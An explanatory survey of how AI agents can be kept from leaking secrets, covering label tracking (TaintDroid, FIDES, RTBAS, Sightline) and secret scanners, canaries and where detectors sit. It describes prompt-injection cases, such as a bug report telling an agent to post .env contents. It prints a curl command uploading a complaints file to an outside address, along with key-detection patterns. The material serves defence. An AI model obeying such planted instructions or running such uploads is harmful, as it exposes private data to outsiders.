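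An approved release can also reveal more than its owner intended. Suppose the owner of the export lets the agent publish the number of complaints each week. A stranger then posts an issue with hidden instructions to count only the complaints from one small island. The published number still looks like an ordinary total, but it now reveals information about a handful of people.

To prevent this, Zdancewic and Myers proposed robust declassification, which requires that an attacker who can influence the system can't learn more than one who only watches it. The weekly count fails this test because the stranger changed what the number meant. For agents that read untrusted text, the condition implies that the system must prevent outsiders from influencing what goes into a message, even if that type of message was approved in advance.

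### What TaintDroid measured

TaintDroid shows how label tracking performs on everyday software. Enck and colleagues modified Android to label data from sensitive sources such as the location sensor, microphone and address book. The system carried the labels through an app's variables, files and messages between apps. When an app sent labelled data over the network, TaintDroid logged the type of data, the app and the destination, but didn't block the transfer.

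The team surveyed 1,100 popular free apps and found 358 that asked for internet access together with access to location, camera or audio data. They picked 30 of these at random and used them by hand for a little over 100 minutes. The phones made 1,130 network connections, and TaintDroid flagged 105 of them. The researchers judged 37 of these to be clearly legitimate, mostly because an app needs to send a location to download the right map. The other 68, from 20 of the 30 apps, were potential misuse. Fifteen apps had sent the user's location to advertising servers. A longer version of *TaintDroid* reports a second study, from 2012, in which a similar fraction of apps potentially misused data.

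A trigger based on permission would have fired on every connection these apps made, because the researchers had selected the apps for their permissions. Tracking the data instead reduced the alarms to about 9% of connections, but roughly a third of those were still false from the data owner's point of view.

The study also found disclosures that a content scanner would probably have missed. Four of the apps sent location data to an advertising company in a binary format, with no readable coordinates. The researchers concluded that the data contained the location because the apps had just received labelled data from the phone's location service. Even readable coordinates are difficult to scan for, since they are ordinary numbers that keep changing.

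TaintDroid doesn't track implicit flows, so a malicious app could use the two-line trick to get data past it. The researchers left out this tracking to avoid false alarms and keep the phone fast. They found no cases where TaintDroid flagged a connection without sensitive data, but they couldn't easily tell how many disclosures it missed because they didn't have the apps' source code.

TaintDroid also had a problem with label creep. The IMSI, a number that identifies a mobile subscriber, begins with codes for the country and network, and Android uses those codes as settings in many internal messages. TaintDroid kept one label per message, so if a message contained a harmless country code, everything else in it was marked sensitive too, and the label then spread to whatever used that message. The team had to turn off IMSI tracking during the study.

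### Guarantees, labels and release

The main advantage of access-based rules is that their guarantees can be proved. Bell's report proves that each operation in the model preserves the rule against writing down to a lower security level. Such a proof doesn't depend on what the text looks like, so it covers a password disguised by an attacker and a customer summary that no scanner would recognise. But it holds only if the system checks every route out. Denning's model, for instance, leaves out signals that a program sends by changing how busy the computer is.

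The proof also assumes that the labels are right, and it is easy to overlook something that needs a label. Bell gives the example of a file whose name is secret. If the folder that lists the name is unclassified, anyone who can open the folder learns the secret without opening the file, so folders need labels too. An agent can pick up secrets the same way when it lists a folder or reads the names of code branches.

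Even correct labels don't determine which disclosures to allow. Enck and colleagues sorted TaintDroid's 105 alarms by looking at server names, the apps' own logs and whether the user had agreed to share the data. Three of the apps had sent the user's location only when the user asked for local content. Blocking every flagged connection would have kept data from advertisers, but it would also have stopped users from getting maps.

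## Tracking sensitive data inside AI agents and the work this blocks

TaintDroid could track a phone's location data through an app because each instruction the app ran had known inputs and a known output. In an AI agent, a language model does much of the processing between input and output, and no program code shows which parts of the context influenced a given sentence.

### Why labels spread through a language model

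Most language models are transformers, which write text in small pieces called tokens. To choose each token, the model uses attention, which gives every earlier token a weight and draws information from it in proportion to that weight. The weights are normally above zero, even for tokens from a file unrelated to the current step, so anything still in the context can influence a later message, if only slightly.

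Xu, Li and colleagues (2026) proved in *Sightline* that ignoring inputs with tiny weights isn't safe, because such an input can still determine the output. A model can also give an input a large weight without using it.

The safe rule is therefore to give each output the join of all labels in the context. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes label tracking through language models as an open problem and this rule as the only safe assumption for now.

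The rule is fairly accurate for a single call to a model. Xu and colleagues studied calls in 2,103 families of open-source repositories and found that only 12–14% of the inputs did not reach the output. An agent's context probably holds a larger share of irrelevant material, because it keeps the results of every earlier step.

### How FIDES works

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a Microsoft system that applies these rules to agents. FIDES is built into the program that runs the agent's tool calls. Its checks are outside the model, so a model that follows hidden instructions can't switch them off.

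FIDES first gives each tool result two labels. The confidentiality label lists the people who may read the result, and the integrity label is "untrusted" if an outsider could have written it. A tool can label parts of a result separately, so the time of an email might be trusted and its body untrusted. When FIDES combines data from several sources, only people who may read every source may read the combined data, and a single untrusted source makes it all untrusted.

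Before each tool call, FIDES compares the labels with a policy for that tool. Costa and colleagues give two basic policies:

- A consequential action, such as a payment, may go ahead only if nothing untrusted influenced it.
- Data may go into a channel only if everyone who can read the channel may also read the data.

The second policy is an access-based trigger. An attacker may still use prompt injection to get the agent to send a message, but the message can't contain data its recipients aren't allowed to read.

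With only these two parts, an agent soon develops label creep. FIDES tries to avoid this by hiding data from the model. When a tool returns something with a stricter label than the current context, FIDES stores it in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name, so the context keeps its old label. The model can still use the name in a later call, such as "send #read_emails_0 to Anna", and FIDES fills in the contents after the model has chosen the call. The policy check then uses the label of the stored data.

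For tasks that need more than forwarding, such as summarising hidden emails, the agent can pass the data to a second model that has no tools. Instructions planted in an email can spoil the summary, but they can't make the second model send anything. FIDES stores the summary in another variable, which carries the joined labels of everything the second model read.

Sometimes the agent needs to know a variable's contents to decide what to do next. Opening the variable adds the contents and their label to the context. To limit this, the agent can ask the second model for an answer in a fixed form, such as yes or no, or one item from a list. The software restricts the second model's output to that form, and FIDES records the form in the label. A policy can then allow a yes-or-no answer from a source whose full text it would block, which is a type of declassification.

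The label doesn't record the number of answers, though. Joining two "yes or no" labels gives "yes or no" again, so the label is the same after one answer as after fourteen, which are enough to reveal a four-digit PIN. A policy that accepts such answers would also need to limit how many it accepts from each source.

FIDES is designed for explicit secrecy, which doesn't cover what outsiders can infer from the agent's choice of actions. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), a formal model of agent programs, identifies this as a particular weakness when data can also serve as instructions, because attackers can then use the agent's choice of actions to leak data efficiently. FIDES also checks only tool calls and treats the final reply to the user as harmless by default. That is reasonable if nobody else can see the reply. But if the chat window loads images from web addresses in the reply, the reply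 can send data to outsiders and needs a check too.

### The coding agent under FIDES

Suppose the coding agent from the earlier example runs under FIDES. Its context begins as trusted and public. The agent opens the settings file, which only B, C and D may read, so FIDES puts the contents into a variable. The agent then runs a public test and posts "The build works on macOS" to the issue tracker. FIDES allows the post because the model has seen nothing private. A simpler access-based trigger would have raised a false alarm because the agent had opened a sensitive file.

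If the agent tries to post the variable itself, FIDES blocks the call because only three people may read the contents, while anyone can read the tracker. FIDES also blocks the call if the agent has the second model summarise the complaints and tries to post the summary, because the summary keeps the export's label. This blocks the description of the pharmacist on the island even though it contains no name or password.

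The harmless post gets through only because the agent hasn't seen the file's contents. If the bug is a wrong port number in the settings, the agent may have to open the variable to find it. From then on, everything it writes is restricted to B, C and D, even the advice "check your port number". The agent could instead have the second model check whether the port is 5432 and use the yes-or-no answer, if the policy allows that. But this helps only if the agent already has a reason to check the port.

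### Tasks completed and attacks stopped

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 user tasks in four simulated settings: an office workspace, travel booking, banking and the chat service Slack. The benchmark has 36 injection tasks, in which text planted in the agent's data is meant to make the agent do something else. The researchers paired each user task with every injection task in the same setting. They used OpenAI's GPT-4o and averaged the results over five runs.

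A basic agent without policy checks allowed 152 injections, not counting cases that the benchmark misjudged. With the checks on, no injections succeeded. FIDES without checks still allowed 21, even though it hid data in variables, because the model could open an untrusted variable and follow instructions it found there.

The zero is less impressive than it sounds because the researchers based the labels on the attacks. AgentDojo has no labels of its own, so they marked a data field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's injections used it. Developers of a real agent don't know in advance which fields attackers will use.

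The checks also stopped a lot of legitimate work. The table shows the percentage of user tasks each agent completed when not under attack. The last column uses o1, an OpenAI model that was better at reasoning.

| Setting | Basic agent, no checks | Basic agent, checks | FIDES, checks | FIDES, checks, o1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0 | 37.0 | 59.0 | 64.5 |
| Travel | 70.0 | 73.0 | 41.0 | 68.0 |
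| Banking | 98.8 | 37.5 | 52.5 | 56.2 |
| Slack | 93.3 | 20.0 | 47.6 | 54.3 |

With GPT-4o, hiding data recovered more than half of the loss in the workspace tasks but only about a quarter in banking. In many banking tasks, the agent must read a file and follow its instructions, such as paying a bill. The file is untrusted, so once the agent opens it, the policy blocks the payment. Costa and colleagues consider most of these failures intended, since an attacker could have written the bill.

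Other failures came from the model. GPT-4o confused variable names and made unnecessary calls. In one Slack task, it asked for a list of channels although the user had named the right one, and the list made the context untrusted. Without policy checks, FIDES completed 23.7% fewer tasks than the basic agent with GPT-4o, but only 6.3% fewer with o1. A better model therefore removed much of the trouble with variables.

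The basic agent with checks gained less from a better model. It completed 37.5% of banking tasks with both GPT-4o and o1, and its Slack score fell from 20.0% with GPT-4o to 17.1% with o1. That makes sense, because a more capable model doesn't make the policy more lenient.

Most of these losses came from integrity labels, so they don't measure how often an access-based trigger for private data raises false alarms. Of the 27 tools with a policy, 21 checked only whether untrusted data had influenced the call. In this test, FIDES also created variables only for untrusted data, not confidential data. In travel, where the basic agent's score didn't fall, many tasks used tools that could run in an untrusted context as long as they didn't violate confidentiality, and no call to these tools violated it.

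The policy for sending messages was also looser than a strict confidentiality rule, because it allowed a message if the recipients were entitled to the data or if the agent had seen nothing untrusted. Costa and colleagues reason that a disclosure in a trusted context is probably intentional. But an agent can paste a password into an email by mistake, and this policy would allow that if no untrusted text had entered the context. The test also did not include answers of a fixed form, because the researchers found them unnecessary for most of the tasks.

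GPT-4o and o1 are long out of date, and some of these attacks no longer work on newer models. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) compares two other systems that control how an agent uses untrusted data, CaMeL and ELBA, on AgentDojo's 105 Slack attacks. All the models it covers resisted every attack even with the policies switched off, so the policy checks had no successful attacks to prevent. Attacks written for newer models might succeed more often.

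Other recent papers try to reduce the work lost to blocks. *APPA* (2026) describes a system that looks for an approved way to continue after a block, whereas simpler systems abort the task. The system completed 64.2–91% of tasks, and no attack succeeded in 1,320 protected runs. The tasks differ from AgentDojo's, so these figures can't be compared with those for FIDES. FIDES has become a baseline for newer systems, for example on the TaintBench scenarios in *Ghost in the Agent* (2026).

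### FIDES in Microsoft's Agent Framework

Microsoft (2026) announced FIDES in *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* as a feature of Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents. According to Microsoft's documentation, the feature is experimental and available only for Python, with a .NET version to follow.

In the documentation's main example, which is close to the coding agent here, an agent sorts reports on a public issue tracker and can also read files and post comments. An attacker files a bug report with hidden instructions to read .env and post its contents. FIDES lets the agent read the file but labels the contents private, which makes the whole run private. The tool for posting comments accepts only public data, so when the agent tries to post, FIDES blocks the call or asks the user to approve it, depending on the settings.

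This version uses three confidentiality levels (public, private and user identity) instead of the research version's lists of readers. Three levels are easier to set up, but they can't express that A may read the complaints and D may not.

The default settings in FIDES protect against injection better than against disclosure. If a developer forgets to label a tool, FIDES treats its output as untrusted but public. Microsoft's claim that a forgotten tool therefore "fails closed rather than open" is true for integrity but not for confidentiality. If an unlabelled tool reads the customer database, FIDES treats the records as public and would let the agent post them on the tracker. Automatic hiding also applies only to untrusted results. A trusted private file goes straight into the context and raises the context's label, so a harmless comment afterwards causes a false alarm.

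Microsoft acknowledges in its documentation that the labels can be too conservative. Once untrusted text enters the context, the rest of the run is untrusted unless the developer explicitly removes it. Microsoft is considering labels for individual messages and labels that relax when the software shortens the context.

The toolkit also has a mode in which FIDES tracks labels without blocking anything. Developers can run an agent as usual and check the log for calls FIDES would have stopped. This is the kind of measurement needed to find false alarms, but neither the announcement nor the documentation includes results from it.

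### Labels based on influence

FIDES reduces label creep by keeping data out of the context. Another approach lets the model read everything and then works out which documents the answer needed. Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, developed a method with four steps:

1. The model answers using the full context.
2. The system looks for a less strict label such that the documents at or below it would have made the same answer almost as likely.
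3. The model answers again, using only those documents.
4. The system throws away the first answer and releases the second one with the less strict label.

To compare likelihoods, the method uses perplexity, which measures how surprising a text is to the model. If the model gives the n tokens of an answer the probabilities p₁ to pₙ, then:

perplexity = (p₁ × p₂ × … × pₙ)^(−1/n)

The system accepts the smaller set of documents if using it raises the perplexity of the first answer by no more than a chosen tolerance, λ. Suppose λ is 0.2 and every token of the answer has a probability of 0.8 with the full context. The perplexity is 1/0.8 = 1.25. If the probabilities fall to 0.7 without the private documents, the perplexity rises by about 0.18 to 1.43, and the increase is within the tolerance. If they fall to 0.5, the perplexity rises to 2, and the answer keeps the strict label.

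In the coding example, the agent may have read both the customer complaints and a public test log. If it writes "Two tests fail on macOS", that sentence is about as likely without the complaints as with them, so the model writes it again from the log alone and the agent can post it. A summary of the complaints would be very unlikely without them, so it would stay restricted.

Siddiqui and colleagues tested the method with two sizes of Llama-2, an older model from Meta. In the most artificial test, each question came with 14 separately labeled documents, which gave over 16,000 possible combinations. The method found the exact right combination for 86% of questions. On questions about pairs of news articles, a less strict label was possible in 647 of 3,465 cases, and the method found it in 57% of these with the smaller model and 39% with the larger one. In 20 short agent conversations where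 a less strict label was possible, the method succeeded in 17 with the smaller model and 19 with the larger one. Asking the model which documents it had used succeeded in 9 and 16, respectively.

The news and agent tests used integrity labels, so they show that the method can separate relevant from irrelevant text, but not how many messages it would remove a confidentiality restriction from. The method also sometimes dropped a document that the answer needed. For the smaller model, this happened in 23% of the news cases where the method relaxed the label. The second answer may be worse as a result, but it still can't contain the restricted text, because the model didn't have it.

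The method therefore protects the second answer even when the system misjudges influence, but it does not protect the choice between labels, which still depends on the private documents. Suppose the agent must post an update about a customer's order. If the customer is overdrawn, the first answer mentions the debt, keeps its strict label and is blocked. Otherwise, the answer is routine and the agent can post it. Someone who knows how the system works could then learn about the debt from the missing update. Explicit secrecy allows this kind of implicit flow.

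The method may also need another call to the model for each possible label. With only "public" and "private" labels, this adds few calls, but if every document has its own label, the number of calls can grow exponentially with the number of documents. An attacker can also add distracting text that prevents the system from relaxing the label, which would leak no data but would stop the agent from doing useful work.

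### Asking the user

RTBAS (Robust Tool-Based Agent System) also looks for the relevant parts of the context, but does so before the model acts. Zhong, Chen and colleagues (2025) designed it as an alternative to asking users to confirm every tool call, which OpenAI's custom GPTs did at the time.

In RTBAS, a screener first marks the parts of the history that matter for the next step. The screener can be a second language model that reads the history, or a small neural network that uses attention scores. RTBAS joins the labels of the marked parts and hides from the main model anything with a label stricter than the joined one. The main model then proposes a tool call. If the joined label satisfies the policy for that tool, the call goes ahead. Otherwise, RTBAS asks the user.

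If a user wants the agent to post on the public tracker that the tests pass, the screener should mark the test log as relevant and leave out the settings file. RTBAS hides the file, and the agent posts without asking the user. If the user wants to post the database settings, the screener has to mark the settings file as relevant. The file's label doesn't allow a public post, so the user has to decide whether to allow it.

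A mistake by the screener doesn't let private data out unnoticed. If it wrongly leaves out the settings file, the main model can't see the file and may fail at the task. If it wrongly includes the file, the user gets an unnecessary question.

Zhong and colleagues wrote 37 test cases about private data in shopping, payments and flight booking. The results give a rough idea of how much work an access-based trigger blocks when the only concern is confidentiality.

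| System | Cases with an unnecessary question | Cases where it should have asked but didn't |
|---|---|---|
| Asks before every call | 11 of 37 | 0 |
| RTBAS with a language model as screener | 3 of 37 | 4 of 37 |
| RTBAS with attention scores | 6 of 37 | 4 of 37 |
| Hides all private data, never asks | 0 | 19 of 37 |

The last column doesn't count leaks. For instance, the system that never asks has already hidden the card number when it reaches the payment page, so the booking fails. That system completed only 35% of the tasks. RTBAS completed 40% or 43%, depending on the screener, even if users refused every request, because it didn't have to ask before doing tasks that needed no private data. Small differences between the systems mean little because there were only 37 cases, all written by the researchers.

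On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, RTBAS stopped every attack that broke its policy. In one case, RTBAS didn't track an injection because it was in text that the benchmark labels as written by the user. Without attacks, the number of completed tasks fell by 10% with the language model as screener and by 7.4% with attention scores. In the Slack tasks, the two versions completed only 22% and 33%. The test had no user to approve calls, so RTBAS skipped every call it would have asked about. More tasks would have been completed if a user had approved the legitimate calls. On the banking tasks, screening roughly doubled both the running time and the cost.

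RTBAS gives the user a say in where private data goes, instead of guaranteeing that it reaches only people who are entitled to it. How well this protects the data depends on whether users read the questions, and the human reviewers in the auto-mode test that Willison reported let most of the dangerous commands through. Users may read more carefully if they are asked fewer unnecessary questions, but Zhong and colleagues didn't test that. The screener's choice also depends on private data, as in the method of Siddiqui and colleagues, so the pattern of questions and completed calls can reveal something about that data.

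### Dropping labels on statistical evidence

Both methods above hide the restricted data before the model writes the version that goes out. It takes less computation to leave the message as it is and drop the labels of inputs that seem not to have influenced it. *GIF* (2026) measures influence by how much small changes to an input would change the model's next token. This measure fails when the model gives one answer a probability close to 1. If a contract makes the model almost certain to answer "no", small changes to the contract barely affect the output, even though the contract decided the answer.

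Xu and colleagues' system, Sightline, learns from labelled examples which attention patterns show that the model used an input. The researchers set a threshold so that, on average, it misses no more than a chosen share of real influences. They tested it on 120 tool calls by an agent under attack in AgentDojo, using Qwen3-8B, a small open model. With the target set at 5%, Sightline missed 3.9% of real influences and removed half of the labels that came from irrelevant inputs. Their versions of GIF and RTBAS's attention screener each removed at most 15.7% of those labels. An integrity policy stopped all 34 calls that carried out an attack.

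A miss has worse consequences here than in RTBAS. If Sightline fails to detect that the settings file influenced a message, the message goes out unchanged, including any password the model put in it. The statistical guarantee also holds only if future calls resemble the ones used to set the threshold. Calls from ordinary work might, but an attacker can look for unusual phrasing that makes the model use a secret without the usual signs.

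### Dividing the work between agents

Developers can also limit label creep by giving the private data to a separate agent. *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) examines how the number of agents, the connections between them and the division of tools affect how much work the rules block. Some features of the arrangement predict the amount of blocked work, with correlations of up to 0.96. Confining sensitive tools to particular agents can reduce that amount.

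In the coding example, one agent could read the exported complaints and write to the support team, while another handled the public tracker and never opened the export. The second agent's label would stay public no matter how many complaints the first one read. But if the first agent sent the second a description of the bug, that description would carry the export's label, so this arrangement works best when the second agent can reproduce the bug from public information.

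## How secrets are detected in an agent's output

Unlike label tracking, a content-based trigger has to recognise a password to stop it from leaving. It can recognise the password from the text alone or by comparing the text with something stored beforehand. Most detectors take outgoing text and return a list of suspicious passages, each with a type such as "AWS key" and often a severity. The safeguard then acts on that list.

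In the coding agent example, suppose somebody chose the database password "bluebell7" by hand. The other thing to protect is the description of the pharmacist on the island who was charged twice in March.

### Known formats

Many services issue keys with a recognisable format. A common type of access key ID at AWS, Amazon's cloud service, is "AKIA" followed by 16 capital letters or digits. A scanner can describe this with a regular expression, which is a formula for a set of strings:

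```
\bAKIA[A-Z0-9]{16}\b
```

The scanner searches the text and returns anything that matches the rule. The \b at each end marks the edge of a word, so the rule doesn't match part of a longer string.

Mishra (2026), in *Boundary-Mutation Testing for Pattern-Based Secret Detection*, notes that a rule using the \b marker depends on the characters around a key as well as the key itself. The marker needs a letter, digit or underscore on one side and something else on the other, so the rule can miss a real key that ends in a hyphen and is followed by a quotation mark. A pattern can also match too much. One rule for SendGrid, an email service, accepts "SG." followed by 22 and then 43 permitted characters, which includes strings SendGrid would never issue.

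Some credentials have two parts. An AWS key ID, for example, comes with a 40-character secret. The secret has no prefix and looks like many other long strings in code, so a scanner can avoid many false alarms by reporting it only when the key ID is nearby. GitHub's *Secret scanning scope* calls these combinations pattern pairs.

The list of patterns needs constant updating, because a scanner can't match a format nobody has added. One batch described in *GitHub adds 37 new secret detectors in March* contained 28 detectors for keys from 15 providers. According to GitHub's documentation, users who think the scanner has missed a secret should first check whether GitHub supports that type.

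### Randomness

Computers generate most keys at random, so a scanner can look for strings that seem random even if it doesn't know their format. The usual measure is Shannon entropy:

H = −Σ pᵢ log₂ pᵢ

Here pᵢ is the share of the string's characters that are the i-th distinct character. Entropy is measured in bits per character, and the scanner flags strings whose entropy is above a chosen threshold.

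The token "k7Qz9fXb" has eight different characters, so each has a share of 1/8:

H = 8 × 1/8 × 3 = 3 bits

In the word "password", the letter s appears twice and six other letters appear once:

H = (6 × 1/8 × 3) + (1/4 × 2) = 2.75 bits

The results are close because a string of n characters can't score more than log₂ n, which is 3 for eight characters. The gap grows with length, so scanners often set a minimum length too.

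| String | Characters | Entropy (bits per character) |
|---|---|---|
| k7Qz9fXb | 8 | 3.00 |
| password | 8 | 2.75 |
| bluebell7 | 9 | 2.20 |
| q7Rz2LmX9vTb4KcW | 16 | 4.00 |
| responsibilities | 16 | 3.08 |
| abcdefghijklmnop | 16 | 4.00 |

The first 16 letters of the alphabet score as high as the random token because the formula counts how often characters occur and ignores their order. The database password has the lowest score in the table. Some strings are random but not secret, such as the identifiers that the version-control program Git gives to commits.

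For these reasons, scanners often use entropy as a backup. One scanner that Mishra tested has 43 named patterns and a single entropy rule, which applies only to strings that no pattern has matched. The scanner assigns medium severity to everything the entropy rule flags, whatever it turns out to be.

### Nearby words

A scanner can also use the words around a string. A typical rule looks for a name containing "password", "secret" or "token", then an equals sign or colon, then a value in quotation marks. It would find the database password in this line, even though the password isn't random:

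```
database_password = "bluebell7"
```

The same rule matches "your-password-here" in installation instructions, so scanners usually have a list of placeholders to ignore. They can also accept lower entropy when a word like "password" is nearby. But if the agent writes "I logged in with bluebell7 and the error went away", the rule misses the password because no such word appears near it.

### Whether a key still works

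Once a scanner has found a possible key, it can test whether the key is still active. GitHub's *Secret scanning* describes validity checks, in which GitHub may contact the service that issued the key. Owners can then deal with working keys first.

A validity check can remove many false alarms, since a made-up key won't work. *Scanning 7.6 Petabytes of HuggingFace Training Data for Secrets* (Ayrey, 2026) reports 221,303 different live credentials from public datasets on Hugging Face, a site for sharing AI models and data. Ayrey's company, Truffle Security, makes the scanner TruffleHog, which includes such a check.

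An unsuccessful test doesn't prove that a key is harmless. For example, a scanner that can't reach a company's internal database can't tell whether the password "bluebell7" opens it. Similarly, GitHub checks whether its own older tokens are valid as part of detecting them, so scanning on its cloud service misses those issued by a company's self-hosted GitHub server.

### Exact matching and fingerprints

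Exact matching searches outgoing text for secrets the owner already knows. The owner registers each secret in a store, and the detector returns the name of any that appears in the text. This works for passwords of any form and for names or account numbers from a customer database.

A store of every password would attract attackers, so the system can keep hashes instead. A hash is a short code that is easy to compute from a value but hard to turn back into that value. The detector cuts the outgoing text into pieces, hashes each one and checks whether the hash is in the store. It has to cut exactly where the secret starts and ends, because "bluebell7." with a full stop has a completely different hash from "bluebell7". An attacker who steals the store could hash common passwords and compare the results with the stored hashes, so the system should mix a secret key into each hash.

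Short or common values cause false alarms. If a customer's surname is Baker, for example, the system may flag output that mentions a bakery's baker. To reduce these false alarms, a rule can require matches on two fields from the same customer record, such as a surname and a postcode. The system can also check output only against stored values that the agent has read in the current session.

Fingerprints extend this idea to whole documents. The detector splits a protected document into overlapping runs of words and hashes each run. It then does the same with the outgoing text and counts how many hashes the two share. With runs of three words, suppose the complaints export contains this sentence:

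> The customer was charged twice for the March order

If the agent writes "Our customer was charged twice for the March order", six of the sentence's seven three-word runs are in the export. That is an overlap of about 86%, so a detector with a 50% threshold would flag it. The detector would miss the paraphrase "A shopper paid two times last spring", which shares no runs with the export. Longer runs reduce accidental matches but make it easier to avoid detection with small edits. The system should ignore standard text such as legal footers, since harmless documents contain it too.

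### Trained classifiers

A classifier learns from examples that people have labelled. It estimates how likely each word or passage in a text is to belong to a category, such as "name" or "home address", and returns those that score above a threshold. Because it uses context, it can learn to label "Jordan" as a person in one sentence and a country in another.

AWS's *AGENTSEC08-BP02 Output filtering for sensitive information* recommends filtering an agent's output with a service called Bedrock Guardrails. The service's filters cover personal data such as names, addresses, phone numbers and financial account numbers, as well as passwords and keys. For data specific to one organisation, such as its own type of case number, AWS suggests training a recogniser on examples and running it before the agent returns its output.

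GitHub also uses AI to find secrets with no fixed format, such as passwords. According to GitHub's *Enabling generic secret detection for AI-detected secrets*, these alerts go into a separate list. GitHub's *Copilot secret scanning for generic passwords is generally available* (2024) describes the first general release, which didn't search issues or pull requests (proposed code changes) and created alerts without blocking anything. It therefore wouldn't have stopped the coding agent from posting "bluebell7" in an issue. To reduce false alarms, that release also skipped code files with "test" or "mock" in their paths, and it stopped reporting new secrets in a file once users had marked five alerts there as false.

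### A language model as reviewer

A second language model can check the agent's message before it is sent. Given the text, the destination and a written policy, it returns a decision, usually with a reason. Unlike a credential scanner, it can recognize that "a pharmacist on the island" could describe very few people. It can also allow the same description in a message to the support team.

However, the reviewer's judgement may vary. Millstone and colleagues used two models to judge disclosures, and when one found a leak, the other often disagreed. The outgoing text could also contain instructions aimed at the reviewer, such as a claim that the customer has agreed to publication. If the reviewer runs on another company's servers, that company receives the sensitive text, which the text's owner may not want.

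Neither the password nor the description of the pharmacist has a fixed format. The table shows whether each method could recognise them in a post on the public tracker.

| Method | "bluebell7" | The pharmacist |
|---|---|---|
| Known formats | No | No |
| Entropy | No | No |
| Nearby words | If the post labels it as a password | No |
| Exact matching | If the password is in the store | No |
| Document fingerprint | As part of a longer copied passage | If the agent copies the export's wording |
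| Trained classifier | Possibly, from the context | Only if trained on such descriptions |
| Language model as reviewer | Probably | Possibly |

### Canary values

A canary is a fake secret that someone plants to find out whether data has leaked. It can be a key to an empty account, a web link that nobody else knows or an invented customer with a working email address. Since the canary has no ordinary use, almost any sign of it deserves attention.

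A canary is a fake secret that can trigger an alarm when it appears in outgoing text. For example, the owner could put a fake key next to the real password in the settings file and have a scanner check outgoing text for that key. If a hidden instruction makes the agent post the whole file, the scanner recognises the fake key and can stop the post. This check misses a post that contains only the real password.

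A planted fake secret can also raise an alarm when someone uses it. The owner only needs to see the attempt to log in or open the link, not the message that leaked the secret. The newsletter tl;dr sec describes a free tool from Tracebit that plants fake AWS credentials to detect attacks on the systems that build and release software.

The security company Dragos used the same idea to find out who reads prompts sent to AI services. *Three breaches, endless leaks* (Moore, 2026) reports that the company planted canaries in two million prompts and found three breaches at providers. *Dragos planted 2m secrets in AI prompts and caught 3 hacked providers* (Constantin, 2026) reports nearly two million prompts, sent between July and November. Each prompt contained unique web links and working credentials, including AWS keys to empty accounts.

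In *Dragos Canary Study* (McDaniel, 2026), each canary appeared in only one request, so any use of it identified the route that had leaked it. This was useful because a request often passes through several companies before it reaches a model. Dragos traced about 2,000 routes.

In the largest breach, attackers copied every request that Dragos sent during a few short periods in late October. The requests contained a couple of hundred AWS keys. The attackers tested some of the keys within hours, looked for more credentials and tried to add their own users. The earliest breach dated from mid-July. None of the three providers knew about the attackers until Dragos told them, and the attackers had almost certainly copied real customers' requests too.

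Canary links gave less clear evidence than keys. *Data processing incidents at the inference providers behind OpenRouter* (2026) describes a Chinese AI lab whose systems opened the links in more than half of the prompts Dragos sent to its models, and in about two-thirds of the requests marked "no data collection" or "zero data retention", a setting under which a provider shouldn't routinely store prompts. MiniMax, a Chinese AI company, later said its security monitoring had extracted links from some requests and automatically opened some of them. The company found no sign that prompts had reached third parties. An opened link therefore shows that something processed the prompt, but doesn't show that the prompt was stolen.

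OpenRouter, which passes requests on to many providers, responded to the findings by removing three of them and withdrawing the zero-retention label from 125 endpoints, the addresses at which providers offer particular models (OpenRouter, *Data Processing Incidents on Inference Providers*, 2026). It is also adapting the Dragos method for regular tests.

According to *Together AI Says Its Own Coding Agent Leaked Customer Prompts* (Faisal, 2026), a related leak began when a coding agent at the AI company Together AI committed a credential to a public repository. The credential gave access to a private store of customer prompts, which an intruder downloaded. The prompts dated mainly from June and July. Five of the credentials in them were decoys that security researchers had planted. The company disclosed the leak on 21 November.

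An alarm that goes off only when someone uses the canary key comes after the data has left. It may never come if the thief keeps the customer records and ignores the keys. A scanner that tests every key it finds will also set off a false alarm, as will an agent that tries the fake key while debugging.

### Where the detector sits

A detector can check only the text that passes through it. If it checks only the agent's final answer, it will miss a password that the agent posted to an issue tracker ten steps earlier. AWS therefore advises developers to send every output through the same filter, including replies to users, messages to other agents, logs, and notes saved to memory. It warns that attackers don't always target the reply to the user.

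Tool calls are the natural place to catch outbound actions, and GitHub's MCP server scans their inputs for this reason. But the input may not contain the data it sends. Suppose the agent runs this command:

```
curl --data @complaints.csv https://example.com
```

The command uploads the complaints export, but its text contains only a file name and an address, so the detector also has to open the file. "git push" contains none of the code it uploads, so the detector has to examine the commits. If the agent starts a program that sends data by itself, the detector may need to inspect network traffic, which is usually encrypted.

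Chat software often displays an agent's final answer while the model is still writing it, so the user, or someone watching a shared screen, may see the first half of a key before the detector has enough text to recognise it. To prevent this, the software has to hold back some of the text until the detector has checked it.

Memory and logs need checks because the agent may read them again in a later session. AWS says its agent memory service removes personal data from long-term records by default but keeps the original content in short-term memory. Developers who aren't allowed to store personal data at all have to filter it out before saving. AWS also recommends logging the filter's decisions, including the type of data, the action taken and the destination. A sudden rise in detections may be a sign of prompt injection.

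Some detectors check text even earlier, before the agent's program sends it to the model. McDaniel of GitGuardian, which sells such a check, argues for this because every company that handles a prompt can read all of it. This check could have kept real keys away from the providers that Dragos found, whereas a filter on the agent's tool calls would not have prevented theft from a provider's servers. But the check may also block a task that needs the model to see the key.

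### Before and after sending

GitHub checks code for secrets at two points. Push protection scans commits as a developer or agent uploads them and blocks the upload if it finds a supported secret. Ordinary secret scanning searches what is already in the repository and creates an alert if it finds a secret.

A check before the agent sends its output can prevent the disclosure, but the agent has to wait for it, and a false alarm stops harmless work. This favours fast methods with few false alarms, such as patterns for known key formats. A check afterwards can take longer, use less certain methods and include human review. GitHub's 2024 password detector ran only afterwards.

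Finding a leaked key afterwards still helps if the owner can cancel it before anyone uses it. GitHub automatically notifies participating services when it finds their keys, so that they can revoke them. But there may be little time to act. McDaniel cites a case that Microsoft observed in which an attacker's AI agent went from scanning GitHub to taking data from a company's store of keys in about five minutes. Deleting the key from the newest version of a file isn't enough, because the repository's history keeps the old version. InfoQ reports that some of the secrets Apiiro found in its study of Claude Code were in repository history.

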